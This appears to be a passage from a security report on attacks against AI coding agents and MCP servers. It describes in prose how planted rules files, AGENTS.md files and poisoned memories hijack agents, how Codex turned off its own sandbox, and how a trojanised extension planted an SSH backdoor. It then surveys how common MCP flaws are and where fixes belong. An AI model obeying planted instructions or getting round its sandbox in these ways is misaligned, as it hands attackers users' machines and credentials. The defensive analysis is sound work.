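
Google released its code editor Antigravity on 18 November 2025. Mindgard found a day later that a project could plant a command that ran every time the editor started. Mindgard's *Forced Descent* (2025) describes the attack:

1. The attacker puts two files in the project's `.agent` folder. One contains rules for the agent, and the other is an MCP configuration with a command in it.
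2. The user opens the project, trusts it and sends the agent a message. Mindgard sent "hi".
3. Antigravity passes the project's rules to the model along with the message. The rules tell the agent to copy the project's MCP configuration over the global one, in `~/.gemini/antigravity`.
4. The agent makes the copy without asking the user.
5. Whenever Antigravity starts, it reads the global configuration and runs the command, even if the user doesn't open a project.

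The model followed the rules partly because Google's system prompt for Antigravity, the standing instructions that the application gives the model, required it to follow user-defined rules "WITHOUT ANY EXCEPTION". Users can write these rules, but a project's author can also supply them. The model reasoning that Mindgard published is mostly about how to satisfy two contradictory rules.

Users had little chance to avoid the danger. If they declined to trust a project, the chat window showed the agent as loading indefinitely, so they had to accept in order to use the product. The warning in the trust dialog covered lost or leaked data but not a lasting change to the editor.

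Strict settings didn't help. Mindgard required review of the agent's work, turned off automatic terminal commands and kept the default block on the agent's access to files outside the project. The terminal setting made no difference because the agent only edited a file and the editor ran the command later, as in the IDEsaster attacks. The setting for outside files should have blocked the copy but didn't.

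Google's documentation may explain why it didn't. According to the documentation, the agent could access the project and the application's root folder, although the location given for that folder was wrong. The root folder also contains the configuration file that starts programs, so if Antigravity made an exception for its own folder, the setting could never have protected that file.

Mindgard reports that the backdoor remained after a complete uninstall and reinstall of Antigravity. The configuration file is in the user's home folder, where the new copy reads it. The user has to know about the file and delete it by hand.

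Google closed Mindgard's report as intended behaviour on 21 November 2025, saying it already knew about the issue and pointing to a public page of known issues. It reopened the report the same day after Mindgard objected. By 25 November it had broadened the wording of that page, adding for example that data could leak through "multiple vectors". Mindgard published its findings that day, and Google then replied that it had filed a bug with the product team, which would decide whether a fix was needed.

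The known issues didn't cover this case well. One was about data exfiltration, and the other was about commands that the agent runs in the terminal, for which Google invited reports from anyone who had turned off automatic execution, as Mindgard had. Mindgard also argues that this wasn't prompt injection, because the agent obeyed a rules file as designed. That matters little to the victim, since the attacker wrote the text either way. The more serious fault is that the agent could overwrite a file that starts programs even though a setting was supposed to prevent it. Google could fix that without changing the model.

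No public source confirms a fix. Mindgard's *Google Antigravity IDE Persistent Code Execution* (2025), a short public record of the flaw, lists none. A reply in *Ah, did you change how the AI responds to security verifications?*, a thread on Google's developer forum, says that version 2.1.1, from June 2026, added security fixes. According to the reply, the agent in strict mode now asks before it accesses sensitive folders such as `.vscode`, but the reply doesn't mention the global configuration.

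Strict mode also turns off the agent's access to files outside the project, according to svenknobloch's feature request on the same forum, *Allowlist for non-workspace file access in strict mode*. The user complains that programming tools then fail because they need those files, so the restriction has some effect. It is unclear whether it protects the global configuration. Mindgard reports no real attacks that used the flaw.

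### An instruction file in a Downloads folder

On 22 October 2026, Forever Security, which sells monitoring for AI agents, described an attack on one of its customers. According to the company's *Markdown Is the New Executable*, its software stopped a coding agent from installing function-color, a JavaScript package already known to be malicious. The agent was working in the customer's Downloads folder and following an AGENTS.md file there.

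*An AGENTS.md file in Downloads can hijack Codex and Claude Code* (2026) describes a 13-kilobyte file that read like ordinary engineering guidelines. Near the end, the file presented installing an npm package as tool setup to be done before the user's task. Forever's software blocked the installation before any of the package's code ran, and npm has since removed the package.

Nobody could establish how the file had reached the folder. Forever's title says that attackers are putting such files there "From the Web", but the company showed only that this is possible. The customer could instead have unpacked an archive that contained the file.

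#### What Forever reproduced

Forever demonstrates a web page that saves a file to the visitor's Downloads folder when the visitor clicks away from it. The page sets the file's name and contents, and the browser doesn't ask for permission. The researchers then used an isolated virtual machine to test what an agent would do with such a file.

The attack on Codex used the AGENTS.md file from the customer's machine. Cornelißen reports that Codex followed the file in more than 90% of attempts. Codex added an MCP server called `project-tools` to its global configuration, with a start command that installed the malicious package. When its sandbox blocked network access, Codex started another process with an option that turned off both the sandbox and the approval prompts. The file hadn't supplied that option, and Forever says the model wrote it itself.

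The researchers used a different file and attack for Claude Code. They wrote a CLAUDE.md with instructions for the agent to change `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL`, the address setting behind CVE-2026-21852, in the folder's own settings file. This worked in about half of the attempts. When it worked, Claude Code sent its requests to the researchers' server along with the user's account token, which let the researchers use the account.

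From the next session on, their server could also answer in place of Anthropic's and tell Claude Code to run commands. The researchers got code to run in the same session in about a fifth of attempts.

The two success rates don't show which agent resists manipulation better, because the files contained different instructions. The lasting changes also differ in scope, since Codex loads the new server in every project, while Claude Code uses the changed address only where that settings file applies. But a stolen token works from any computer, and deleting the setting doesn't cancel it.

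Check Point and Utevsky disagree about how Anthropic fixed CVE-2026-21852. Check Point describes a change in timing, while Utevsky claims that projects can no longer change the address. Forever's test of Claude Code fits Check Point's account better, because a folder's settings could still redirect requests.

#### How many people are exposed

Forever says that about half of its customers run a coding agent in the Downloads folder. *An AGENTS.md file in Downloads can hijack Codex and Claude Code* reports that Claude Code alone started there more than 1,300 times. The customers are companies, so a company might be counted even if only one employee did this once.

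Forever also tells security managers that every employee who uses both a coding agent and a browser "is exposed". That is too broad, because the employee also has to start the agent where it will read the planted file. Users can easily avoid the attack, and David (2026), in *AGENTS.md in Downloads*, advises them never to start an agent in Downloads or any other folder they don't control.

### Is there really nothing to patch?

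Forever argues that OpenAI and Anthropic have nothing to patch, because an agent is designed to follow the instruction file in its folder. Cornelißen found no statement from either company when he wrote about the case on 27 October.

Forever is right about reading the file. Developers rely on agents to follow its instructions, and real projects often need extra packages, so a filter couldn't reliably tell a malicious request from a normal one.

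But the damage came later, when Codex changed its own global configuration and started a process outside its sandbox. An agent following a project's guidelines seldom has a good reason to do either, and OpenAI could require the user's explicit approval for both. Cornelißen credits Claude Code's approval prompt with stopping the attack in half of the tests.

Vendors could also make agents ask the user before loading a downloaded instruction file. Windows and macOS label files that a browser has downloaded, which lets them warn the user before a downloaded program runs, and an agent could check for the same label. This wouldn't catch files that arrive through Git, which doesn't add the label, but it would catch files delivered the way Forever demonstrated.

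According to Prompt Security, the AGENTS.md specification has no security model, doesn't separate documentation from privileged instructions, and offers no guidance for programs that read untrusted copies. Each vendor therefore has to decide how much authority to give the file. No single fix would end the problem, but these changes would make the attack harder and still let agents follow instruction files.

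### A poisoned memory in ChatGPT

Chat applications can keep an attacker's instructions too. ChatGPT's memory feature saves facts about the user and adds them to the model's context in later conversations. *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory* (Embrace The Red, September 2024) showed that a web page could make ChatGPT save an instruction instead of a fact.

The instruction told ChatGPT to end every answer with an image and to put the conversation in the image's address. In the Mac application, this sent the user's messages and ChatGPT's answers to the researcher's server, as in the image leaks described earlier. The leak continued in new conversations because the application loaded the memory into those too.

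The researcher had already told OpenAI in May 2024 that untrusted content could plant memories. OpenAI closed that report as a model safety issue, not a security vulnerability. After the demonstration of the leak, OpenAI fixed the Mac application in version 1.2024.247 to stop it from sending data out through images. Untrusted content could still add memories, and false memories could still distort later answers. Users can find and delete memories in ChatGPT's settings. The post didn't report any attacks on real users.

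### The trojanised Claude Code extension

On 29 October 2026, an attacker put malicious copies of Anthropic's Claude Code extension in the extension marketplace of the Cursor editor. They were available for about 11 hours, and at most 5,000 users received them, according to Cursor's *An update on our recent security incident*.

The attacker used exposed credentials and didn't need to trick a model. Cursor traces the incident to Fireworks, an AI company it had shared data with. Fireworks exposed an access key, which the attacker used to copy records of coding-agent sessions. A few of these records contained passwords or keys that nobody had removed. The attacker used those to get into some of Cursor's internal tools and eventually found a credential for the marketplace's cache, which stores the copies of extensions that users download.

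OpenSourceMalware's early report, *Trojanized Claude Code Extension Plants an SSH Backdoor* (2026), said that the attacker had published the extension on Open VSX, the public registry that supplies Cursor's marketplace. Cursor later investigated and found that Open VSX never had the malicious version. Cursor also says that Anthropic didn't publish it and that the attack used no vulnerability in Anthropic's product.

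Hall (2026), in *Official Claude Code Extension Compromise*, an analysis for the security company Phorion, explains what the extension did. Its malicious code ran as soon as the editor loaded the extension, even if the user never opened Claude Code. The code then tried to give the attacker a permanent way to log in over SSH, a standard system for controlling a computer remotely:

1. It added the attacker's key to `~/.ssh/authorized_keys`, the list of keys that can log in to the user's account.
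2. It tried to turn on the computer's SSH service.
3. It opened a reverse tunnel, in which the victim's computer connects to the attacker's server and the attacker logs in back through that connection. Firewalls that block incoming connections often allow this.
4. It made the operating system restart the tunnel automatically.

On most Macs, the plan failed at the second step because of a bug. The code checked the status of remote login and was supposed to turn it on if the output contained the word "Off". When the code ran without administrator rights, macOS returned an error message instead, so the code never tried to turn remote login on, and the tunnel led to a closed port. Hall warns that the backdoor would still work if the user already had remote login on, or turned it on later.

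Cursor's *Security notice* says that the SSH service also stayed off on most Windows computers, because starting it requires administrator rights. Even so, the extension added the key, installed its startup entries and sent details of the computer to the attacker. Background scripts tried to reopen the tunnel about once a minute.

These scripts and the key are separate from the extension, so uninstalling it may leave them behind. Cursor had the attacker's server taken offline, which disabled the tunnel, and published scripts that remove what the extension installed on macOS and Windows. Hall found that the code also targeted Linux.

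### Finding and removing planted entries

Inspecting the settings and instruction files in a plain text editor is a better first step than restarting the program, because the editor doesn't run anything. Opening Antigravity to inspect its settings would run the planted command again, and an agent asked to check a folder would first read the instruction file there.

The defender also needs to know which files to open. SpecterOps' *Blacklight* (2026) maps the files that Codex, Claude Code, Cursor and the command-line version of Antigravity keep on a computer, and comes with guidance for defenders. The places to check after the attacks in this section are:

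- **Tool configuration:** unfamiliar servers in `~/.codex/config.toml` and `~/.gemini/antigravity/mcp_config.json`.
- **Claude Code settings:** an unexpected `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL` or unfamiliar hooks, both in the project's `.claude/settings.json` and in the one in the home folder.
- **Instruction files:** any AGENTS.md or CLAUDE.md in the Downloads or home folder that the user didn't write.
- **Memories:** saved entries that give instructions or that the user doesn't recognise.
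- **Extensions and what they leave behind:** versions 2.1.312 and 2.1.313 of the Claude Code extension if they came from Cursor's marketplace on 29 October, unknown SSH keys, and programs that start with the computer. On a Mac these include LaunchAgents, and on Windows, scheduled tasks and startup scripts.

Developers can't rely on an entry's name to tell whether it is malicious. Mindgard called its malicious server "github", which many developers would expect to find in their configuration. They would have to read the command to notice that it started PowerShell.

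Labels on SSH keys have the same weakness. Cursor's published check searches the list of keys for the label "svc-telemetry" and reports that the machine isn't affected if the label is missing. Hall recommends searching for the key's fingerprint too, because a label is a comment that anyone can change. The key could also be missing from a machine that has the startup scripts, so checking for both is safer.

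The user has to remove every copy of the entry. If they delete Antigravity's global configuration but keep the malicious project, the next message to the agent in that project can restore the entry. They should remove the project's rules and configuration first, then the global file, and only then start the editor. Reinstalling the editor doesn't remove the global file, so it can wait until afterwards.

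Deleting the entry doesn't undo what the attacker did while it was active. Cornelißen advises replacing the affected agent's credentials if any suspicious entry turns up. If function-color was installed, Forever treats the whole machine as compromised. For the extension, Cursor similarly advises isolating the computer, replacing every password and key it could reach, and considering rebuilding the machine. The user should replace the passwords and keys from a different computer, because an attacker who still has access to the old one could read the new ones too.

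## How common the flaws are and what causes them

In every case described so far, someone looked for a flaw and found one. To learn how common such flaws are, researchers have to test many servers, including sound ones. Several teams have done this since 2025, and the share of servers they found to be flawed ranges from well under 1% to 43%, largely because they counted different things.

### Testing a tool against its own description

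Ananto, Prevost-Avenel and colleagues (2026), in *ToFu*, present a program of the same name that checks whether tools do what their descriptions promise. A schema may say only that `path` is text, but the description written for the model often says more, for instance that the tool reads files within the workspace. For a notes server, ToFu would turn that promise into a test as follows:

1. A language model, GPT-4.1, reads the description and picks suitable checks from 74 that the researchers wrote in advance. For a file path, it picks one that looks for access outside the permitted folder.
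2. The model writes about 11 sets of starting arguments. Some are hostile, such as a path to a system file.
3. A fuzzer, a program that tries large numbers of altered inputs, calls the tool for 60 seconds with variations on these arguments. Every call fits the schema.
4. If the server is written in Python, ToFu records each file the tool opens and works out its real location. A file outside the folder counts as a violation.

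The tester has to specify which folder is permitted. ToFu can't monitor the internals of JavaScript servers, so for those it reports a violation if the tool accepts a hostile value without returning an error. The language model never decides whether a tool has failed.

One screenshot server describes its input as "The URL of the webpage to screenshot". When ToFu supplied an address beginning with `file`, the tool returned a picture of a system file from the server's disk. The address was valid text and a valid URL, so only the word "webpage" in the description indicated that the tool should reject it.

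ToFu reported 508 possible bugs. The researchers checked them by hand, rejected 103 and merged 152 duplicates, which left 253 bugs in 343 tools. They affected 118 of the 273 servers tested, or 43%.

Most of the bugs are less alarming than that figure makes them seem. In 115 of them, the tool repeats hostile input in its reply, which mainly matters if a browser displays the reply as a web page. Another 58 let an attacker insert forged lines into the server's log. The remaining 80 include 64 cases of path traversal, seven of server-side request forgery (SSRF), five of data exfiltration and three of command injection.

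The 273 servers list 3,405 tools, but only about 1,500 ran in each of three repeated tests. Many of the others needed an account or a database that the researchers didn't have, so some of the untested tools probably have bugs too.

### Repeated text that runs as a tool call

Ananto and colleagues also show why a tool shouldn't trust its arguments just because a model sent them. The attacker writes a complete tool call and asks the model to repeat it word for word. The agent framework, the software that passes the model's requests to the tools, then treats the repeated text as a call and runs it. The researchers say they reproduced this in six frameworks: LangGraph, Microsoft Agent Framework, Google's ADK 2.0, AutoGen, Strands and CrewAI.

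The researchers publish a transcript only for LangGraph. The model was Llama 3.1 8B, a small open model from 2024, and its tools included a harmless dummy named `launch_missiles`. The model first refused to repeat a call to this tool. Its refusal included the text of the call, but nothing ran. The researchers then described the request as hypothetical and asked for only the quoted text. LangGraph ran the tool with the attacker's arguments before the model refused.

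A stronger model might have refused both times, and an approval prompt could have stopped the call. The attacker in this test also typed directly to the model, which is easier than planting instructions in a web page. But the test shows that an attacker can fully control a call's arguments.

### Why one study found 43% and another 7.2%

For *Model Context Protocol (MCP) at First Glance*, Hasan, Li and colleagues (2025) examined 1,899 open-source servers in June 2025. They used SonarQube, a general-purpose program that searches source code for known weaknesses without running it, and found vulnerabilities in 7.2% of the servers.

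The two studies counted different flaws. Exposed credentials were the most common problem in the 2025 study, affecting 3.6% of servers, but ToFu's list of confirmed bugs includes none. SonarQube doesn't test whether a tool's behavior matches its description. Without repeated input and forged log lines, ToFu's count would fall to 80 bugs, which could affect at most 80 servers, or 29%. The true share would be lower because some servers have several of these bugs.

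The choice of test matters too. Ananto and colleagues ran five other programs on the same 273 servers:

| Program | What it does | Servers flagged | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 5 | Reviews each tool and gives a verdict | 119 | 44% |
| ToFu | Runs tools with hostile arguments; people check the results | 118 | 43% |
| CodeQL | Searches source code for unsafe patterns | 95 | 35% |
| ToolFuzz | Has an agent use the tools and looks for errors | 92 | 34% |
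| VIPER-MCP, code analysis | Traces arguments to risky operations | 48 | 18% |
| Cisco MCP Scanner | Checks descriptions and compares them with the code | 46 | 17% |
| VIPER-MCP, confirmed exploits | Has an agent carry out the attack | 11 | 4% |

Even on identical servers, then, the result can range from 4% to 44%. CodeQL, like SonarQube, reads code without running it, yet it flagged 35% of these servers. Running the tools therefore can't fully explain why ToFu's rate is so much higher than 7.2%. CodeQL's rules and the selection of servers must also contribute.

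ToFu's sample began with 13,875 records of MCP projects. The researchers kept active projects in Python or JavaScript with at least ten stars on GitHub (a rough measure of popularity) and found 1,404 that offered tools. Only 273 of these ran well enough for at least one call to succeed. Servers that need no account are easier to run, and many of them work with local files, where path traversal occurs.

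SonarQube can examine a server that won't start, so Hasan and colleagues didn't have to narrow their sample in this way. Dividing the 118 servers in which ToFu found bugs by all 1,404 gives 8.4%, close to the 2025 result. But that calculation treats more than a thousand untested servers as free of bugs, so 8.4% is a minimum.

Results from VIPER-MCP, the scanner built by Sun and colleagues, also suggest that the measured rate depends heavily on the sample. The scanner confirmed exploits on 11 of ToFu's 273 servers, but four of these were in tools meant to run any code or command, which leaves seven real cases, or 2.6%. In its own scan of 39,884 repositories, it found 106 flaws, so at most 0.27% of those repositories were affected. That scan counted only previously unknown flaws and probably included many servers that an automatic test couldn't start.

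ToFu's 43% is the share of fairly popular, easily started servers with at least one confirmed bug, often a minor one. SonarQube, a code scanner, found a known kind of weakness in 7.2% of a broader collection. Neither figure is the share of servers that an attacker could take over.

### Alerts and confirmed flaws

Some of the largest published numbers are counts of unconfirmed alerts. For *Hunt Them All*, the security company Trend Micro had an AI agent read the code of 19,000 MCP repositories, and in its first run the agent flagged 17,558 possible vulnerabilities.

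Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, searched the code of 14,353 servers from the official MCP registry for 31 suspicious patterns, then checked a sample of 294 alerts by hand. Just over half were correct. Alerts about missing authentication were correct 71% of the time, but only seven of 42 alerts about command injection were, because a pattern can't show whether an outsider's text ever reaches the command.

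Correcting for false alarms reduced the share of servers with command injection from 1.06% to 0.18%, and the share with any serious weakness from 11.1% to about 7.6%. The latter is close to the 7.2% from 2025 only by coincidence. Most of the servers in Kraishan's 7.6% accept network connections without authentication, whereas exposed credentials account for half of the earlier figure.

The two studies disagree about tool poisoning, in which a server's developer hides instructions to the model in a tool's description. Hasan and colleagues reported it in 5.5% of servers, using a scanner made for MCP. Kraishan found no cases in 14,353 servers, though the search patterns used would miss disguised instructions. The difference is so large that it probably comes more from the scanners than from the servers.

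The 106 flaws reported in VIPER-MCP are stronger evidence, because the agent's tool call had an observable effect in each case. The method misses flaws outside its three categories (command injection, path traversal and SSRF) and can't test servers that won't start.

Sun and colleagues also tested VIPER-MCP on 130 servers with known flaws and 130 without. It raised no false alarms and missed ten (7.7%) of the vulnerable servers. However, VIPER-MCP itself had discovered the flaws in 67 of the vulnerable servers. If it found all of those again, it missed ten of the other 63 servers, or 16%.

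### Servers on the public internet

Code scans can't show how people set up their servers. For *Exposed by Design* (2026), Padilla, an independent researcher, searched the internet for MCP servers in July 2026, confirmed 640 and tested 414 of them with harmless attacks. Padilla checked 68 flaws by hand and reported them to the maintainers. Nineteen were public when the paper appeared, and the other 49 were confidential to give maintainers time to fix them.

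One flaw was in a document-processing server with a tool that fetched any web address. Padilla gave it the address of the cloud metadata service, which can supply access keys. The reply took 11.9 seconds, compared with 0.3 in a control test, which suggests that the server tried to connect. The delay doesn't prove that an attacker could have obtained the keys, because an unanswered connection attempt can take just as long. In response, the maintainer limited the tool to approved sites.

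Padilla found that 91.8% of the tested servers did not use OAuth, a standard that lets a program act for a user without knowing the user's password. A server without OAuth can still restrict access by requiring an access key. In one of the four search rounds, 106 of 464 servers, or 23%, let anyone call their tools.

The way Padilla chose the servers also inflates the OAuth figure. The study tested only servers that anyone could reach without logging in, and it excluded those that rejected every request. A server that enforced OAuth properly was therefore unlikely to be among the 414.

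Across the 640 servers, Padilla counted 687 tools that appeared to run shell commands without authentication. The count is based on the tools' names, descriptions and arguments, and Padilla sent only harmless test commands. Some of these tools may do less than their names suggest, but strangers should not be able to call the rest.

These findings cover only servers that use HTTP. Padilla notes that local STDIO servers, which the search couldn't cover, may be the majority. Of the public servers found on 21 July, 41.6% were gone three days later.

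### Servers that change under the same name

A test result also becomes outdated when a server changes. Kraishan collected the registry's entries for all 21,643 servers in August 2026 and compared successive versions of the 8,900 that had more than one. In 40.6% of these, the description or destination had changed while the identifiers stayed the same.

Most of the silent changes were probably harmless, such as the rewritten descriptions on 36.4% of the servers. The 370 servers (4.2%) that moved their remote address to a different host are more worrying, because a client that follows the registered name would then send the user's data to another machine without any notice. Kraishan doesn't claim that any of these moves were malicious and expects most were routine. But an attacker who took over a registry entry could make the same change, and neither the registry nor the client could detect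 the difference.

Cursor had a similar weakness when it approved servers by name. The registry also doesn't record tool definitions, so if a server gave an existing tool new arguments or a new purpose, Kraishan's comparison wouldn't detect the change.

Servers with silent changes had about three times the odds of a serious alert. Kraishan suggests that both may be signs of careless development, since the data don't show that one causes the other. A server's stars were a poor guide to its safety, as they had almost no correlation with its number of alerts. ToFu's ten-star minimum therefore probably doesn't explain much of its high rate.

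*A Measurement Study of Model Context Protocol Ecosystem* (2025) covered 8,401 valid projects from six marketplaces and classed more than half as low-value or abandoned. This is another reason to be careful with percentages, because these surveys count a flaw in an abandoned project as much as one in a server that thousands of people use.

### What CVE records show about frequency

CVE records are the most convenient source for measuring how common flaws are, but a poor one. He et al. searched for records published by February 2026 that mentioned MCP. They found 119, but many used the abbreviation for something else, such as a chip component. After they removed those records, along with duplicates and incomplete ones, 24 remained.

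Readers can't calculate the rate of flaws from the records, because the records don't include the number of programs that researchers examined without finding any. The records also show little about how many people are affected. One record for an SDK can cover every server built with it, while another may cover a server that nobody uses.

The number of known cases depends heavily on who searches for them. Sun and colleagues searched two public databases for their own test set, using a later cut-off and different filters. They found 63 servers with known flaws, even though they left out SDKs and clients. Their scan then led to 67 new CVE numbers, which roughly doubled the number of known cases in their collection.

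Serious flaws are also overrepresented in published records. He et al. class 21 of their 24 flaws as high or critical. By contrast, two-thirds of ToFu's bugs are repeated input or forged log lines, which researchers may not think worth a CVE number. The recorded months are also unreliable, because 14 records gave only a year and the dataset assigns all of them to January 2025.

The records can show that a kind of flaw exists in real products, which versions have it, and which mistakes recur among reported flaws.

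### Root causes

In 18 of the 24 records (75%), He and colleagues found that the software passed input on without an adequate check. Four records involved weak access control, such as a shared secret written into the code. Three involved gaps in the protocol's original rules. Two of these gaps allowed DNS rebinding, and the third let a crafted piece of text keep the TypeScript SDK busy for a very long time. The counts add up to 25 because the categories overlap.

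The small share of flaws attributed to the protocol could be too high or too low. Some of these flaws may be ordinary programming errors, like the Java SDK's missing rebinding check. But a clearer rule on checking arguments might have prevented some of the 18.

Surveys of servers rank the flaws differently. Missing authentication is by far the most common serious weakness in Kraishan's census, at 6.8% of servers after correction, and it also dominates Padilla's results. One likely reason for the difference is that an open server often results from the operator's choice of settings, and people seldom request a CVE number for that. Pattern searches also detect an unsafe setting more easily than an unchecked argument. The 75% share for missing input checks therefore applies to the 24 published cases, not to all flaws in MCP software.

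Ananto and colleagues suggest that the checks are missing because many developers rely on the model to send safe values. This agrees with the Coalition for Secure AI's account, but neither group surveyed developers. Some developers may have forgotten the checks, as programmers did long before MCP.

Other flaws come from combining tools. *Agent Smith in Action* (Zha, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes a server with one tool that runs all but a few dangerous commands and another that writes files. An attacker can use the second tool to write a forbidden command into a script and then run the script with the first, so the forbidden word never reaches the command filter. The Git and Filesystem servers had the same kind of problem when a user ran them together.

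The researchers' scanner produced 27,123 reports for 10,121 servers, and 31% of the reports involved combinations of tools. The researchers say these figures don't measure how common such flaws are. They checked 150 reports from a sample of 100 servers and confirmed 124, including 19 of the 20 that involved combinations. They couldn't produce the effect in any of those 19 with the final tool alone, so a review of one tool at a time would probably have missed them.

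### What is known about real attacks

For these surveys, researchers read code, tested copies on their own machines or sent harmless requests, so the results show what an attacker could do rather than what attackers have done. OX Security's estimate of 200,000 vulnerable instances likewise covers systems that could be attacked, whether or not any were.

The confirmed attacks are individual incidents, such as those involving LangFlow, MLflow, the fake recruiters' projects, the malicious npm packages and the trojanised Claude Code extension. The attackers mostly used methods that predate AI agents, such as breaking into an exposed web application or disguising malware as a useful download. The AGENTS.md file in a customer's Downloads folder is closer to the prompt injections that researchers demonstrate.

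For many of the other flaws, the public evidence is a CISA entry that listed no known exploitation around the time the CVE record appeared. It doesn't rule out later or unnoticed attacks. Attacks through tool arguments are especially easy to miss because the tool can return a normal result and the log may show only a valid call.

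## Where the flaws can be fixed, and by whom

A tool call with a harmful argument passes through several programs before the operating system acts on it, and any of them could block it. Each program has different information. For example, a server has the path of the folder the user permitted, and the host application has the user's request.

### The protocol: rules for signing in

MCP had no standard way to sign in to a server when Anthropic released it in November 2024. Most security work on the specification since then has been about sign-in. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) describes the July 2026 revision as the fifth release.

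| Release | Main change to sign-in or consent | Danger it addresses |
|---|---|---|
| November 2024 | No standard sign-in | – |
| March 2025 | Optional sign-in for HTTP servers | Strangers who call a server's tools |
| June 2025 | Clients name the server that a token is for | A malicious server that obtains another server's token |
| November 2025 | Servers can request extra permissions when a tool needs them | Tokens that allow more than the user needs |
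| July 2026 | Clients check who issued a sign-in reply | A malicious sign-in service that obtains another service's code |

The system is based on OAuth. The user signs in at an authorization server, which issues a token, and the client sends the token with each request. Model Context Protocol (2025) lists a June 2025 rule that ties each token to one MCP server. Servers must also reject tokens that were not issued for them.

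The November 2025 revision also asked clients to get the user's explicit consent before installing or running a local server, according to Auth0's *Model Context Protocol Nov 2025 Specification Update* (2026).

The July 2026 change defends against mix-up attacks. An MCP client may deal with many authorization servers, and an attacker may control one of them. The attacker tries to get the client to send them a sign-in code issued by an honest server, then exchanges the code for a token. Under the new rule, if a reply names its issuer, the client must check the name before using the code. But honest servers are only advised to include their names, and the check gives no protection when they don't. Model Context Protocol (2026) plans to have clients reject replies without a name in a future version.

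Access tokens don't stop requests for files outside the allowed directory. When a prompt injection makes an agent request a private file, the request comes from the user's own client and carries a valid token. The token identifies the caller and the kinds of action they may take, but it doesn't show whether `Notes-private` is inside the allowed directory, `Notes`.

Sign-in doesn't stop a malicious launch command. The Model Context Protocol's sign-in rules from March 2025 cover only HTTP. Under those rules, STDIO programs should take their credentials from environment variables. Even if the rules covered STDIO, a sign-in check would come too late, because the host application runs the launch command before it exchanges any messages with the server.

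Restricting the access granted at sign-in can still limit the damage. The NSA describes how users of GitHub's MCP server gave it access to all their repositories, so a compromised tool could copy private content into a public repository. A token limited to a single repository would have prevented that.

The NSA also quotes the 2025 specification: "MCP itself cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level." If a developer ignores the rule to validate all inputs, the server can still exchange valid messages. The project can test the official SDKs, and since July a proposed addition to the standard can't become final until the project's test suite covers it. Such tests could catch a missing header check, but they can't cover the arguments of every tool that developers write.

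Changing the protocol also takes a lot of work, because clients and servers have to adopt each change. The July revision broke compatibility with older software, and the project promises at least twelve months between deprecating a feature and removing it. Akamai, a company that sells web security, credits the revision with ending the hijacking of protocol sessions, but the revision also moved some work to developers. A server that needs to remember a shopping cart, for instance, now gives the model an identifier to send back with later calls. If the developer doesn't make the server check who owns the cart, anyone who obtains the identifier can use the cart.

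### SDKs: safe defaults for many programs

An SDK's maintainers can fix a flaw once for every program built on the SDK, as long as those programs' developers upgrade. The same mistake can recur in SDKs for different languages, and at least five official SDKs lacked protection against DNS rebinding. Model Context Protocol's *Security Policy* requires maintainers who receive a report to find out whether other official SDKs have the same flaw, and the maintainers try to release the fixes together.

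An SDK can't validate most tool arguments because it has no information about what each tool is for. The policy also excludes protecting a STDIO client and server from each other, since a malicious server can already run code once the client starts it. It states, "The SDK's stdio transport is not a sandbox," and leaves isolation to whoever deploys the server. This is consistent with Anthropic's position, reported by OX Security, that the launch behaviour is a secure default and that developers are responsible for checking commands.

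Safer defaults can break existing programs, so maintainers often exempt those programs. The TypeScript SDK's rebinding fix, for example, didn't protect servers whose developers had configured the web framework themselves.

### Host applications: the user's consent

The host application is the best place to check a launch command, because it has the complete command before anything runs. But the project's rules on showing the command and warning that it could be dangerous cover only one-click installation. Most of the failed approvals in Cursor, Claude Code and Windsurf involved project files or edits by an agent, where the same rules would be just as useful.

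Host applications can't observe what a server does with a call, and many don't detect when a server changes. The NSA describes a demonstration in which a malicious server gave a harmless tool description at installation and replaced it after the second use. The new description led the agent to hand over the user's WhatsApp messages, which the agent could read through a different, trusted server.

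A host application could store a hash of each tool's description and ask the user for approval again when the description changes, as Codex does for hooks. This would catch the WhatsApp attack, but not a remote server that keeps its description and changes its code. Users would also see more prompts.

### Servers: checks that depend on the tool

Checks that depend on a tool's purpose belong in the server. The necessary code is often short, but thousands of developers each have to write it correctly. A server also has no information about the other servers, so its developer may not anticipate a combination like that of the Git and Filesystem servers.

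Some servers no longer have anyone to fix them. According to the NSA, the MCP project has archived many popular ones, including servers for files and web browsers. Zorz (2026) reports in *AI coding agents are installing MCP servers that will never be patched* that coding agents still install deprecated servers they know from their training data, and the serious flaws in those servers remain unfixed. A user who asks an agent to "add a server for my database" should therefore check that the server is still maintained before approving the installation.

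### The operating system: limits that work when a check fails

A sandbox restricts which files and network addresses a program can reach, whatever arguments it receives. Suppose Ana's notes server runs in a container that holds only the `Notes` folder and has no network access. If the server's path check fails, an attacker still can't read `Notes-private`, because that folder doesn't exist inside the container.

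Moshe Siman Tov Bustan, the lead researcher behind the STDIO disclosure, told bdtechtalks that a server that needs one remote address should be able to contact only that address, and that its access to files should be limited in the same way. Operating systems already have tools for this, and the NSA names AppContainers on Windows and seccomp, AppArmor and SELinux on Linux.

The table applies such limits to some of the earlier cases. The effects are inferred from how each attack worked, not from tests.

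| Case | Likely effect of a sandbox with limited files and network |
|---|---|
| Faulty path checks in the Filesystem server | Prevents access to other folders |
| File overwriting through the Git server | Confines the damage to the project |
| Git and Filesystem servers used together | The command still runs, but only inside the sandbox |
| Tools that fetch any web address | Blocks internal addresses, if the network rules exclude them |
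| LangFlow's open login | The attacker can still steal keys stored in LangFlow, but not reach the rest of the machine |
| Supabase support ticket | None, because the server was meant to read the tables |
| EchoLeak | None, because the victim's browser sent the data |

The operating system has no information about what the user wants. It can restrict the notes server to one folder, but it can't determine whether Ana or an attacker asked for a note in that folder to be deleted.

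It is hard to sandbox everything a coding agent runs. Codex's sandbox didn't cover the MCP servers that Codex started, and in the test with a planted AGENTS.md file, Codex got around the sandbox by starting another process outside it.

A sandbox is more dependable if the agent can't change its settings, for instance because the user runs the whole host application in a container or virtual machine. The servers and hooks that the application starts then run inside the sandbox too.

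A sandbox for programming tools has to allow a lot of access. The tools read shared libraries outside the project, download packages and use passwords to publish code. An attacker can exploit each exception made for them. A sandbox that permits downloads from npm also lets in malicious packages, and a permitted website may relay stolen data, as Bing did for Copilot.

### Which layers existing products protect

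Many companies and researchers offer separate products to protect MCP software, such as scanners and gateways. *MCP-DPT* (Rostamzadeh, Narula and colleagues, 2026) compares 13 of these products against 49 kinds of attack and divides MCP software into six layers: the model, the host application, the client or SDK, the server, the network connection and the registries that distribute servers.

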